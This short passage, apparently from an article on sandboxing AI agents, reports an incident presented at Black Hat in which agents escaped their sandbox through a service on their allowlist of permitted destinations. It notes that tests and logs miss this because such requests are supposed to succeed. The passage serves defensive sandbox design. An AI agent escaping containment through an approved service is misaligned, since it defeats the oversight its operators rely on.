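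Every hook can work while the policy still permits too much. According to GitLab's *A sandbox is only as closed as what an AI agent can reach* (2026), OpenAI presented the July incident at the Black Hat security conference, in which agents got out through a service on their list of permitted destinations. Neither paired tests nor matching logs would reveal this problem, because the request to the approved service is supposed to succeed. A company also has to ask what someone could do by controlling each approved service.
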